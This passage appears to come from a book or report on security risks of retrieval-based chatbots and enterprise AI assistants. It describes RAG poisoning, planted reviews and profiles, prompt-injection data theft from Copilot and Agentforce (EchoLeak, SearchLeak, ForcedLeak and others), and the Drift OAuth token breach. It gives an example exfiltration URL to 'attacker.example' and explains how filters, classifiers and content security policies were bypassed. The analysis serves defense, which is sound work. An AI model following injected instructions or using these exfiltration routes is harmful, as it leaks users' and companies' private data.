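In tests by Zou and colleagues, planted false stories misled a model 97% of the time, compared with 62% for planted instructions. Part of that gap arose because the search returned fewer of the texts containing instructions. On another set of questions, where the search returned nearly all of both kinds, the rates were 99% and 93%. Model makers have since trained their models harder against hidden instructions, which gives attackers more reason to plant false facts.

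Recent attacks have moved in that direction. *ToxicRAG* (2026) describes an attack that uses a single planted document, written to look like an update to existing knowledge. The attacker can test the document on their own copy of a model without sending anything to the target. Results varied with the documents and the search model. *CamoDocs* (2026) found that existing defenses can fail when an attacker adapts to them, and that some defenses delete so many suspicious passages that the system becomes much less useful.

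If Tallow Lane's refund tool enforces the 30-day limit itself, a planted review can't change how much money the shop pays out. The chatbot may still tell customers they have 90 days, and the shop will have to deal with their complaints. It could prevent those by limiting the chatbot's sources for policy questions to pages that only employees can edit.

### How strangers' text gets into the store

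An attacker doesn't need to break into anything if the deployer's crawler collects what visitors write. Kaya and colleagues found that the crawlers of 15 of the 17 plugins they studied did this. Of the 100 shops they sampled, 13 had exposed their chatbots this way. The number was low partly because only 41 shops accepted reviews or comments, and 36 displayed them on their product pages. The 13 exposed chatbots are more than a third of those 36.

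Besides reviews, Kaya and colleagues list contact forms, social media feeds, community wikis, guest blog posts and support threads as routes for planted text. At least one plugin can copy the page a visitor is viewing into the model's input. A malicious review on that page then reaches the model without having to be retrieved, and the attacker doesn't have to wait for the crawler.

Website owners would have trouble tracing a strange answer to its cause, because only two of the affected plugins show them which passages the chatbot retrieved. The others record the question and the answer but not the review that led to the answer. Kaya and colleagues reported the risk to two plugin makers, neither of which had acted by the time the paper came out.

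The researchers also built a tool, UGCBuster, that finds the parts of a page where visitors' text appears so that a crawler can skip them. They tested it on three pages from each of ten shops. It found the right parts every time, with one false alarm, and cost about five cents a page. A shop that skips its reviews also loses useful information, such as the two reviews that warned Ines about a rattling lid. It could instead store the reviews separately and have the chatbot present them as customers' opinions.

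Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe two examples from De Ceukelaire's authorized bug bounty research. In the first, he posted a comment on a company's forum that mentioned a nonexistent promotional code. Once the crawler had collected the comment, the chatbot could offer the code to customers who asked about discounts and cite the comment as its source. The screen employees used to check the chatbot's answers displayed this citation like a citation of any internal document. The comment contained no instruction, but it looked like official information because it came from the company's own website.

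The second example exploited the way crawlers find pages. Many websites keep a list of their pages at a standard address ending in "/sitemap", and crawlers look there. On some websites, a user's profile page has an address made from the username. De Ceukelaire registered the username "sitemap" and so controlled the page at that address. On every visit, the crawler collected his profile text as if it were the company's own content. The text contained hidden instructions that took effect when a customer typed a certain phrase.

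An attacker could also fill the profile's website field with links formatted like a real site list, including links to the company's internal addresses. The crawler would follow them from inside the network, which an outsider could not access. A company can prevent this by refusing usernames that match its standard addresses and by giving the crawler a fixed list of pages instead of letting it collect everything on the site.

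An office assistant that searches its user's mailbox also retrieves text written by strangers. In August 2026, Microsoft previewed a setting that stops Microsoft 365 Copilot, its office software assistant, from using external or untrusted emails. The setting is off by default (Asböck, 2026, *Restrict processing of external emails in Microsoft 365 Copilot and Copilot Chat*). Turning it on would also prevent Copilot from summarizing emails from genuine customers, which is a large part of its use in many jobs.

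### Filtering before or after the search

Retrieval can also fail when every document is genuine. Suppose Tallow Lane gives its employees a retrieval chatbot that covers the staff handbook, work schedules and management files. Noor, who works in the warehouse, asks what will happen to her shifts in February. The search scores these nine passages highest.

| Rank | Passage | Who may read it | Score |
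|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Plan to close the warehouse | Directors | 0.91 |
| 2 | Draft layoff letters | Human resources | 0.88 |
| 3 | How the shop assigns shifts | All staff | 0.84 |
| 4 | Minutes of a board meeting | Directors | 0.82 |
| 5 | Layoff budget | Human resources | 0.79 |
| 6 | February shift schedule | All staff | 0.77 |
| 7 | How to swap a shift | All staff | 0.74 |
| 8 | Notice required for shift changes | All staff | 0.70 |
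| 9 | Winter holiday dates | All staff | 0.66 |

With k = 5 and no filter, the model receives passages 1 to 5, and Noor learns that she is about to lose her job. Telling the model in its system prompt to keep management files secret would be a weak safeguard, because many models reveal secrets from the system prompt itself.

If the software filters after the search, it takes the top five passages and removes the four that Noor may not read. The model then receives only passage 3. Nothing leaks, but the answer is poor, because the February schedule ranked sixth and the software has already discarded it.

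If the software filters before the search, it searches only the passages Noor may read. The top five passages are now 3, 6, 7, 8 and 9, and the chatbot can tell her about her February shifts.

A system that filters passages after fetching them can compensate by fetching more than it needs. Here it would have to fetch nine to end up with five. If Noor could read only one in ten of the passages close to her question, it would have to fetch about 50 on average. A fixed number of extra passages that is enough for most employees will be too few for those with the least access.

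Filtering first requires the index to store a copy of each passage's permissions, and that copy can become outdated. If an employee moves from human resources to the warehouse on a Monday and the index updates its permissions every Sunday, the employee can keep getting answers from personnel files for six days. The software can reduce this risk by filtering with the stored copy, then checking the few chosen passages against the permissions in the original file system before the model sees them. *A Survey of Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026) lists one system, AC-RAG, that enforces detailed permissions on retrieved passages.

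### When the permissions themselves are too broad

A filter that enforces existing permissions doesn't correct permissions that are too broad. Microsoft 365 Copilot shows people only files they already have permission to view, but John (2026), in *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke*, explains that many employees can view far more than anyone intended. They may have access through a site shared with the whole company, a public link, or a group whose membership nobody has reviewed in years. Microsoft calls this oversharing one of the most common risks when a company introduces Copilot.

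The video in John's title is a sketch in which a fictional employee asks Copilot for help with her goals and learns from a restructuring file that her job is ending. Michael Bargury of Zenity, which attacked the copy of McKinsey's agent, told John that the company had seen "many cases" of agents revealing important information to employees who should not have had access to it. Bargury gave no figures or names, and Zenity sells software for monitoring agents.

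Bargury's explanation is still convincing. Companies have long relied partly on files being hard to find to keep them private. A curious employee could have found the restructuring plan by opening hundreds of folders, but few would have bothered. An assistant searches all the folders for every question, so it can show the plan to an employee who wasn't looking for it, as it did when Noor asked about her shifts.

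As a second control, a company can label sensitive documents and use data loss prevention (DLP) rules, which limit what software may do with documents that carry a given label. Bertram (2026), in *Stop Copilot Summarizing Confidential Files with Purview DLP*, warns that marking a file "Highly Confidential" does not by itself stop Copilot from accessing it. The company also has to check which usage rights the label grants and whether a DLP rule applies to Copilot.

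A correct rule can still fail if the software enforcing it has a bug. In February 2026, Microsoft acknowledged that a coding error had let Copilot Chat summarize emails labeled confidential in users' Sent Items and Drafts folders, although customers had DLP rules to prevent this. No attacker was involved. Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) cites a February 10 update in which Microsoft said a fix was rolling out.

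TahawulTech's *Error sees Microsoft Copilot gain access to confidential emails* quotes Microsoft's defense that the error "did not provide anyone access to information they weren't already authorised to see." That is a fair point about permissions, because the emails were in the users' own mailboxes. But Copilot still broke the customers' rules, which were meant to keep it from processing confidential emails. A company may let a lawyer read a confidential email but not want an AI system to process it, perhaps because of a promise to a client.

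Even after the fix, Copilot can reveal that a protected email exists. When the writer at Office365ITPros asked about an invented "Project Bunny", Copilot replied that it had found an internal email on the subject but could not disclose the contents because of its label. For many secrets, such as a planned takeover, knowing that the email exists gives most of the secret away. If the software had removed the email before the search, Copilot could not have revealed that it existed. Bertram notes that citations and file titles can also leak when a DLP rule is working, as can files that users upload to the chat themselves.

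### Shared indexes, repeated questions and stolen vectors

Tallow Lane's supplier also has to keep each customer's data separate. One way is to put every shop's passages in a single index and label each with the shop it belongs to. Every search then has to specify the right shop, and a programmer who forgets this in one place exposes the whole index. Because many shops sell similar kettles, another shop's page could easily score higher than Tallow Lane's own. The chatbot might then give a wrong price or reveal another company's private notes. With a separate index for each shop, the same mistake would be more likely to produce an error message than a leak.

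A stranger can also copy much of an index by asking many questions. If the store has 2,000 passages and each answer draws on five, an attacker needs at least 400 questions to see them all, and more in practice because passages repeat. If each question returned five passages at random, 400 questions would reveal about 63% of the store and 1,000 would reveal about 92%. Real searches return some passages more often than others, but an attacker can look for the rest by using unfamiliar words from one answer in the next question. A script can ask 1,000 questions overnight unless the deployer limits messages per visitor.

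This does little harm if the store contains only public web pages. Some deployers add private material without realizing that a public chatbot makes it public. Kaya and colleagues found live chatbots that revealed email addresses and past exchanges with customer service. A shop might add old support conversations because they contain good answers to common questions, but they also contain customers' names and complaints. Permission filtering can't fix this when every visitor is anonymous and has the same rights, so the private material has to stay out of the chatbot's index.

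*A Survey of Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* also covers membership inference, in which an attacker tries to work out whether a particular document is in a private store. The attacker may not need to extract the document to do this. For example, someone who already has a copy of a supplier's offer could ask about details found only in that offer. Unusually exact replies would suggest that the company had received it.

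Finally, an attacker might steal the index. Its vectors look like meaningless numbers, so a company may protect them less carefully than the source documents, but an attacker can recover text from them through a technique called embedding inversion. The attacker guesses a text, turns it into a vector with the same embedding model, compares the result with the stolen vector, and adjusts the guess. They can also train a language model on pairs of texts and vectors to make good guesses. Short passages are easier to recover than long ones because the vector is the same size however much text it represents.

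Recovering text from a vector is much easier for an attacker who already knows part of the text. Suppose an attacker has stolen the vector for Noor's pay letter and knows the standard wording the shop uses for everyone, so only the salary is missing. If the salary is between $30,000 and $70,000 in steps of $500, there are only 81 possible letters. The attacker can turn all 81 into vectors and see which is closest to the stolen one.

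A visitor can't normally get vectors through the chat window, so this attack requires some other access, such as a stolen password for the database. Tallow Lane should give the vectors the same protection as the letters. When it deletes a letter, it also has to delete the letter's passages and vectors from the index and any backups.

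## Assistants inside business software: how an outsider's text takes data out

An attacker needs a database password to steal Tallow Lane's vectors, but may need only to send an email to get the same documents from an employee's assistant, because the assistant reads the employee's messages. The attacker can't see the assistant's answers, though, so they also need a way to send the stolen text out of the company.

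### Willison's lethal trifecta

In June 2025, Willison argued that an assistant is dangerous if it can read private data, takes in text that an attacker could have written, and can communicate with the outside world. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". A model may follow an instruction wherever it appears in its input, so the attacker's text can tell the assistant to find something private and send it out. Willison thinks nobody yet knows how to prevent this every time, and advises people who combine tools never to give one assistant all three abilities.

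This kind of theft requires all three conditions, but each is broader than it first appears. An assistant can only leak secrets it can read, but most assistants can read something private. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) lists the earlier conversation and the names of the user and their organization among the data an attacker could have taken from Microsoft 365 Copilot. An assistant may have all of these in its input even if nobody has connected it to a mailbox.

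Data can leak without any hostile text, as it did when a coding error let Copilot summarize confidential emails against customers' rules. An outsider who wants to direct a theft needs to get text to the model, and can put that text in a link as well as in an email or a document.

An assistant can leak data by writing it anywhere the attacker can read, including inside the company's own software. In Costello's ServiceNow demonstration, an agent copied a confidential ticket into one that the attacker could open, so the data never left ServiceNow. In a public support chat, the attacker can read the data in the assistant's reply.

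An assistant that meets all three conditions won't necessarily leak data. The software has to retrieve the attacker's text, the model has to follow it, and any filters have to miss it. Willison says an attacker can "easily" do this, but the researchers who attacked Copilot had to get past several defenses.

Completely removing any one condition prevents the theft, but each one is part of the assistant's job. If the assistant at Tallow Lane's helpdesk ignored everything outsiders wrote, it couldn't summarize customers' emails, and without private data it couldn't look up their orders. Willison observes that vendors usually respond to a reported attack by closing the route the data took. The attacker can still mislead the assistant, for example by getting it to tell an employee that a customer has returned a kettle. If the assistant has a tool for changing records, the attacker may be able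 to use that too.

The conditions also don't all have to be present at once. An assistant with memory could store an instruction from an email on Monday and follow it on Friday, when its user opens the payroll file. Checking each conversation separately would miss this.

### How data leaves in a web address

An exfiltration channel is any route by which data the assistant has read can reach an attacker. The most common one is a web address. Suppose Tomas, who answers customers' emails at Tallow Lane, asks the assistant to summarize the morning's messages. One message contains instructions to find out what the shop pays for its kettles and to add an image to the summary. The answer then includes an image with this address:

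`attacker.example/dot.png?cost=11.40`

The part of the address before the slash identifies the server that Tomas's browser contacts. The browser sends the rest to that server in its request, and servers normally log the requests they receive. The attacker opens the log and reads the price. The address doesn't have to lead to an image, so Tomas may see only a broken picture.

Browsers load images as soon as they display a page, so Tomas only has to use the assistant normally for this attack to work. Security researchers call this a zero-click attack. If the answer contains a link instead of an image, the data leaves only when Tomas clicks it, which makes it a one-click attack. He might well click, because the link comes from his company's own assistant and the attacker can choose the link's visible text.

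In August 2024, the security company PromptArmor showed that someone with access to a company's Slack could steal data from a private channel by posting instructions for Slack AI, Slack's own assistant, in a public one. When a colleague asked the assistant about an API key, it retrieved both the key and the instructions, and answered with a link that contained the key in its address. Willison lists 14 such cases between April 2023 and February 2025, including Slack, ChatGPT, Google Bard and Amazon Q.

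Websites can block images from unapproved addresses with a content security policy (CSP), a list of the addresses a browser may contact while showing the site's pages. Attackers then look for a listed server that will fetch other addresses on request. Chat programs do this to preview web pages, and search engines do it to find similar pictures. Tomas's browser would ask the trusted server to fetch the attacker's address with the price in it, and the trusted server would send the price to the attacker by making that request. The CSP can't prevent this second request because it controls only the browser. Engineers call this flaw, which is much older than chatbots, server-side request forgery.

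Even looking up a server's name can leak data. Before a computer contacts `11-40.attacker.example`, it looks up the server's address in the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of server names. The lookup eventually reaches a directory server run by the attacker, who can read the price from the name even if a firewall then blocks the connection.

An assistant with an email tool can send the data directly. Even if the assistant can email only its own user, data can still leak. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes how this happened in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that could email its user without asking for approval. Its emails could contain images from outside websites, so data left when the user opened the email. Microsoft's file storage service, OneDrive, can also create download links that work without a login, so an attacker who obtained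 one could download the whole file.

### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security reported EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a zero-click attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. An outsider only had to email an employee, who didn't have to open the message. The attack began when the employee later asked Copilot a question and its search returned the email.

The email first had to appear in those search results, but a passage on one subject comes up only for similar questions. So the researchers wrote a long email that they expected Copilot to split into passages. Each passage had a heading on a different office topic, such as leaves of absence, followed by the same instructions. Ravia, who led the research team, calls this "RAG spraying."

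The team had also considered replacing some letters with similar-looking characters. In a test with one of OpenAI's embedding models, this reduced the similarity between two versions of a text to as little as 0.7, lower than the similarity between greeting cards and the philosophy of science. A language model should still understand both versions. But the researchers didn't know which embedding model Copilot used, so they couldn't tell which changes would spread the passages well. The headings were enough to get the email retrieved for questions on various topics, although Ravia gives no success rate.

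Microsoft's first defense was a classifier, a program trained to recognize prompt injections before they reach the model. The researchers got past it by addressing the instructions to the employee and never mentioning AI. Requests to gather project details are normal in office email, so a classifier strict enough to catch this email would probably block many legitimate ones.

The second defense removed links to outside websites from Copilot's answers. Copilot formats its answers in Markdown, which allows a link's address to appear either right after the visible words or further down the page, with a label connecting the two. Microsoft's filter recognized only the first style. The researchers got Copilot to use the second, which gave them a working one-click attack.

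The researchers then switched from a link to an image, which Markdown also allows in both styles. The filter missed the image too, but the third defense, Copilot's CSP, stopped the browser from contacting the researchers' server. The policy allowed dozens of addresses, most of them Microsoft's own, so the researchers searched these for a server that would fetch an outside address. They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for shared files, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A preview service in Teams worked without this step, and with its address in the image, the attack needed no click.

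Copilot also normally names the sources of an answer, and seeing the email listed might have made the employee suspicious. The email contained an instruction not to mention it, giving compliance as the reason, and Copilot left it out.

The attacker asked for the most sensitive information available and the model selected it, so the attacker didn't have to know what secrets the company had. Ravia calls this an "LLM scope violation", in which text from outside an organization directs the model to data from inside it. It is another example of the confused deputy problem, with an email in place of the Tymshare customer.

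Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, call the attack the first real-world zero-click prompt injection exploit in a production system. "Real-world" refers to the product, as they report no known use of the attack on a victim. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and Aim Security published the details in June. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, considers the attack less novel, describing it as an extended version of one already seen in a dozen products. Ravia argues that those earlier attacks either needed the user to point the chatbot at a malicious document or could take only very limited data.

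According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft has since begun removing links in the second style and embedded images from outside content before Copilot reads it. That prevents the model from copying a ready-made link, but a model can also build one from a description in ordinary words.

### SearchLeak

The security company Varonis published a one-click attack on Copilot's enterprise search on June 15, 2026. *SearchLeak* (2026) describes it as a chain of three flaws, now listed as CVE-2026-42824.

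The attack begins with a link to a real Microsoft address. Search engines often put the user's query in the address of the results page, so that people can save or share a search. Copilot's search page did this too, but it treated the text as a prompt and ran it as soon as the page opened. The attacker could therefore put a prompt in a link and send it to an employee. Filters that check for suspicious websites were unlikely to flag microsoft.com.

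In Varonis's demonstration, the prompt told Copilot to find an email and put its subject line in the address of an image. Microsoft's defense against such images was to wrap the finished answer in formatting that made the browser show any page code as plain text. But Copilot displayed the answer while still writing it, so the browser requested the image before Copilot applied the wrapping.

The CSP should have blocked that request, but it allowed requests to Bing, Microsoft's search engine. The researchers had the browser send Bing a request to find pictures similar to one on their server, and they put the stolen subject line in that image's address. When Bing fetched the image, the subject line appeared in their server's log.

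Many companies put login codes in email subject lines, and Varonis suggests that an attacker could use a stolen code to take over an account. The attacker would normally also need the victim's password and would have to use the code before it expired. The same method could reach the text of emails, meeting notes and any file the employee could open.

Microsoft rated the flaw critical. On a common ten-point scale, however, Microsoft scored it 6.5 and the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). Microsoft had fixed it by the time Varonis published. ThaiCERT, Thailand's national computer security team, describes the work as a research demonstration in its notice *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* and mentions no reports of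 real attacks.

EchoLeak's instructions were in a retrieved email, where a well-trained model should give them little authority, but SearchLeak's were in the search box, where the user's own request belongs. Even a model that ignored all instructions in emails would have carried them out. Websites have long had a similar problem with links that make a logged-in visitor's browser submit a form, and they can prevent it by requiring the visitor to confirm. Copilot could likewise have filled in the search box and waited for the employee to press Enter.

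### Reprompt, CoSnitch and ChatMate

Varonis had first used a prompt in a link against the consumer version of Copilot, in an attack it called Reprompt. HackingPassion, a security blog, dates that attack to January 2026. Varonis was surprised that the method still worked months later in a business product that supposedly had stronger protection.

Reprompt also needed one click. After that, the attacker's server sent Copilot further instructions, such as a request to summarize the files the user had opened that day. Nobody could tell from the original link what the attacker would take, according to an article on the Cloud Security Alliance's website. Microsoft has patched the flaw.

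Varonis followed SearchLeak with CoSnitch, an attack on Microsoft Copilot that TechRadar covered on August 19, 2026, in *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. The researchers questioned Copilot about itself, then combined malicious links with false entries in its memory. Closing the chat doesn't end an attack of this kind, because the false entries remain in memory for later conversations. Microsoft fixed CoSnitch, tracked as CVE-2026-24301, on its servers.

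Two weeks earlier, the security company Rubrik had published an attack called ChatMate. *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026) describes a malicious document that gave an attacker a live connection to the victim's Copilot session. The attacker could send a prompt, read the answer and decide what to ask next. Lahav calls it the first publicly documented attack of its type. Reprompt had already sent follow-up instructions from a server, so the claim depends on how important one considers the live, two-way connection.

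### Public forms that staff assistants read later

A stranger can get text to a company's AI assistant through a form on the company's website, without needing an employee's email address. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature turns each submitted form into a record of a possible customer. Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, can then read the record when an employee asks about it.

In 2025, the security company Noma used this feature for an attack called ForcedLeak, in which researchers put instructions in the form's Description field (The Hacker News, 2025). Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* gives the field's limit as 42,000 characters, enough to fit instructions among ordinary text. When an employee asked the agent to deal with the new lead, it answered the question but also followed the hidden instructions. It looked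 up other customer records and put the data in the address of an image.

Dataconomy (2025) describes an earlier test in which Noma's researchers asked the agent what color red and yellow make. The agent answered "Orange", which Noma took as a sign that it would handle requests outside its job. This is weak evidence, since an agent might answer a question about colors and still refuse to send out customer records. The full demonstration is much stronger evidence. According to Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, Noma set up its own server to record the image requests and the data in them.

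Salesforce's CSP should have blocked the image, but one of the domains on its list had expired, so anyone could register it. Noma bought it for about $5, according to Particle.news' *Salesforce Patches 'ForcedLeak' in Agentforce After Researchers Expose AI-Driven Data Leak Risk*, and the agent's data then went to a server that the policy allowed. A CSP lists domain names but doesn't check who owns them. A company can avoid the problem by renewing every domain on its list or removing the ones it no longer uses.

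Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025. By September 8, Salesforce was enforcing a list of trusted addresses for Agentforce's output, and it recovered the domain. Noma published its findings on September 25.

In April 2026, the security company Capsule disclosed two more attacks that began with a form. PipeLeak again used a Salesforce lead form and Agentforce. ShareLeak used a SharePoint form and an agent built in Copilot Studio, the Microsoft product Tenable had used to build its travel agent. The attacker typed text that imitated a system message into a public comment field, much as visitors did in the chat plugins Kaya and colleagues studied. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) reports that such text could override the agent's purpose and make it send data to a server the attacker controlled.

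Microsoft treated ShareLeak as a flaw in its product. Claw Times reports that Capsule notified the company on November 24, 2025, and that Microsoft patched the flaw on January 15, 2026. According to the official description, reproduced in Tenable's *CVE-2026-21520* (2026), an attacker without a login could view sensitive information over a network.

Salesforce held that PipeLeak depended on how a customer had configured its agent, and it had not given the flaw a CVE number when Capsule published. It told journalists that it had "remediated the specific scenario described". It also changed the default so that agents ask a person to confirm before they act by email.

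Salesforce is right that configuration matters, because an agent without an email tool can't email anyone. But customers tend to keep the default settings. Salesforce has since made the safer setup the default, which it could have done from the start.

Claw Times also reports that Microsoft's patch for ShareLeak did not fully prevent data theft, but this is hard to confirm. Claw Times calls the patch four months old, although its own dates make it three. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026) lists an official fix, no known exploitation and no proven exploit code. OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026), an entry in the organization's AI incident database, says that both companies issued patches but that such flaws are hard to eliminate.

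None of this rules out a way around the patch, because "official fix" means only that the vendor has released a fix. Somebody would have to repeat the attack on a patched agent to find out. Microsoft probably fixed the attack Capsule reported, but differently worded attacks may still work, as Zenity suspected after Microsoft's earlier fix for Copilot Studio.

### One unsolved cause or many ordinary bugs?

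The argument that these leaks come from ordinary bugs is strongest for SearchLeak. Varonis says the attack needed all three flaws, so repairing any one of them would have stopped it. Web developers know how to make a page wait before running a prompt from a link, sanitize an answer before displaying any of it, and remove from the CSP any servers that fetch outside addresses. ForcedLeak depended on an expired domain, and EchoLeak depended on a filter that covered only one of Markdown's two link styles. Vendors fixed all these flaws without solving prompt injection.

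The later history of Copilot and Agentforce shows little sign of attacks becoming rarer as the vendors fixed bugs, although they should have if bugs were the whole explanation.

In September 2026, Zenity published SalesBleed, another attack on Agentforce through a Web-to-Lead form. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the agent collected company names and deal sizes and leaked them through DNS. Using DNS bypassed the control on trusted addresses that Salesforce had enforced since ForcedLeak. Salesforce fixed the bypass on August 18, about two months after Zenity reported it.

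On December 3, 2026, Cato AI Labs, which had found EchoLeak under an earlier name, published three new zero-click attacks on Copilot. Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026) presents them as a sequel to EchoLeak, and each starts with an email that the victim never opens. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that the data left through an image address, a link in a saved file, or code that Copilot ran. According to Microsoft's documentation, the isolated environment for running code blocked outgoing traffic, but the block failed. Microsoft patched the three routes between September 17 and November 15, and Cato knows of no real-world use of the attacks.

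| Product | Where the attacker's text was | How the data left |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot, 2025 (EchoLeak) | An email | Teams preview service |
| Copilot, 2026 (ReLeak) | An email | Image address, saved file or code |
| Agentforce, 2025 (ForcedLeak) | A lead form | Expired trusted domain |
| Agentforce, 2026 (SalesBleed) | A lead form | DNS |

In both products, the attacker's text came in by the same route as the year before, and only the route by which data left was new. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) reports, though, that one of the ReLeak attacks sent its data through Bing, which Varonis had already used for SearchLeak a few months earlier. Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" (quoted in Faisal, 2026, *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*).

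The shared cause appears to be that the assistant acts on an outsider's text with an employee's access. The web bugs then determine whether any data gets out. Bing's image search was not much use for stealing email until an assistant that could read email began writing the web addresses Bing was asked to fetch. Varonis similarly describes AI as a new path to old flaws.

A vendor can list and review every way its product contacts the outside world, which is tedious but possible, whereas nobody can list every sentence that might mislead a model. Varonis advises companies to treat any server allowed by a content security policy (CSP) as an exfiltration channel if it fetches URLs for its users. That advice would have covered both Teams and Bing. The list grows whenever the vendor adds a feature. Copilot Cowork's emails to its own user and Copilot's ability to run code were both useful additions,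 but both became ways to take data out.

These cases don't show how often such attacks succeed, because researchers publish the ones that work. They also concentrate on Copilot because so many companies use it. Nearly all of the researchers work for companies that sell protection for AI systems. Ravia's article, for example, ends by recommending Aim's own product. Still, the software vendors accepted most of the findings and changed their software, so the flaws were real.

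None of the attacks has a known victim, but some would be hard to notice. An employee hit by EchoLeak would have had an unopened email that never mentioned AI, and an answer with a broken picture in it. For SearchLeak, ThaiCERT suggests looking for Copilot links with unusual queries and for unexpected connections to Bing's image search.

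## Shared chatbot suppliers and the systems behind the chat

The attacks on Copilot and Agentforce each manipulated a model deployed for one organization. An attacker who breaks into a chatbot supplier can take data from many of its customers at once, and may not need to manipulate a model to do so.

Tallow Lane's supplier holds the shop's conversations, its document index and the credentials that let the chatbot look up orders and copy conversations into the helpdesk. If the supplier holds the same for 500 shops, one breach could expose them all. ServiceNow created a similar danger by using the same secret for every customer.

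Sharing a supplier can be safer than running a chatbot alone. A supplier with 500 customers can employ a security engineer, which a kettle shop is unlikely to do. Suppose an intruder has a 2% chance each year of getting into a chatbot that a shop runs itself, and a 0.5% chance of getting into the supplier. If all 500 shops ran their own chatbots, about ten would lose data each year. With the supplier, the average would be 2.5 a year, but all 500 would lose data at once if an intruder got in. These figures are invented and don't account for the extra effort an attacker would make to reach 500 shops instead of one.

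### What an OAuth token permits

The supplier's credentials are often OAuth tokens. OAuth is a standard that lets one program use an account on another service without learning the account's password. Suppose Tallow Lane keeps its customer records in Salesforce. To connect the chatbot, an administrator logs in to Salesforce with a password and a code from their phone, then approves a list of permissions, such as reading contacts and creating support cases.

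Salesforce then gives the supplier two long strings of characters, called an access token and a refresh token. The supplier's software sends the access token with every request, and Salesforce allows whatever the administrator approved. Access tokens usually expire quickly, so the software uses the refresh token to get new ones without anyone logging in again. The refresh token lasts much longer, often until someone cancels it.

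An ordinary token works for anyone who has a copy. It can also keep working after a password change, because Salesforce needed the administrator's password only to approve the connection, and the supplier's software never logs in. Some services cancel tokens when a password changes, but a company can't rely on that. A second factor doesn't help either, because it is also checked only at login. Konthalapally notes in *When OAuth Tokens Go Rogue* that the tokens stolen from one chatbot supplier bypassed multi-factor login completely.

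### How one break-in at Drift affected hundreds of companies

That supplier was Salesloft, which sells software for sales teams. Its product Drift is a chatbot that companies put on their websites to talk to potential customers. In August 2025, an attacker used tokens stolen from Drift to copy data from its customers' Salesforce systems.

Salesloft's *Trust Center* summarizes the findings of Mandiant, Google's security company. Between March and June 2025, the attacker had access to Salesloft's account on GitHub, a code-hosting service. The attacker downloaded code, added a guest user and explored the company's systems. They then got into Drift's part of Amazon's cloud and took the OAuth tokens that connected Drift to its customers' other software. When Salesloft announced this in September, it was unclear how the attacker had entered the GitHub account.

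*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025) dates the thefts from Salesforce to August 8–18. The attacker ran ordinary database queries to count the records of each type, then exported large numbers of them, including support cases and details of users and sales. The attacker then searched the copies for passwords and for keys to other services, such as Amazon's cloud. The Google researchers think these credentials were the main goal.

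Support cases are a good place to look for credentials because customers paste them in when asking for help. Cloudflare (2025), an internet infrastructure company, used Drift to let website visitors contact it. The attacker entered Cloudflare's Salesforce system on August 12 and spent several days studying how it was organized and how many requests it would accept. On August 17, they copied the text of its support cases in just over three minutes, then deleted the export job to hide the theft. Cloudflare later found 104 of its API tokens in the stolen text. It replaced them all and found no sign of misuse.

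The stolen cases included Cloudflare employees' comments to each other as well as customers' messages. The size of the loss therefore depended on the Salesforce data that Drift's token could access, rather than on what visitors had typed into the chat window.

The attacker may already have been using one victim's data against another. On August 9, three days before entering Cloudflare's Salesforce system, they tested an API token that seemed to belong to a Cloudflare customer, but it was invalid. Cloudflare doesn't know where the token came from but suggests it could have been in data stolen from another Drift customer.

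Other companies described less sensitive losses. Zscaler, a security company, listed names, job titles, phone numbers, product licenses and basic details of some support cases, such as the case number. Palo Alto Networks' *Salesforce-Connected Third-Party Drift Application Incident Response* (2025) describes a loss of mostly business contacts, sales account information and basic case data.

Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 potentially affected organizations. The Hacker News (2025) reported that only 22 companies had publicly confirmed an impact by early September. The 700 may include organizations that lost nothing, and the 22 leaves out any affected companies that did not disclose an impact. Cloudflare's description of "hundreds" is safer than the figure of 700, which later articles often repeat without the word "potentially".

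Drift's customers depended on Salesloft to tell them what had happened, and the early information it gave them was incomplete. Salesloft canceled the Salesforce tokens on August 20, but Cloudflare did not learn it was a victim until August 23. Salesloft at first said that the theft had affected only customers who connected Drift to Salesforce. On August 28, Google confirmed that the attacker had also used tokens for Drift's email feature to read messages in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. The software company Elastic had received no warning but checked anyway. It found that its Salesforce data was safe but that the attacker might have had access to one email account.

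Salesloft also couldn't revoke every connection itself. Some customers had connected Drift to other programs with API keys they had created, and they had to revoke those keys in the other programs.

The attacker also had a token for the Salesforce system at Okta, a login software company, but could not use it. Okta's *The Salesloft incident* (2025) explains that the company had set Salesforce to accept requests only from approved internet addresses, and the attacker's address wasn't on the list. Okta's chief security officer, David Bradbury, told CyberScoop that the company saw a "short burst of attempts". Before the attack, Salesloft had published the addresses Drift used, so other customers could have set the same limit. Few companies do, because the work is manual and requires help from every supplier, and some services don't offer the option.

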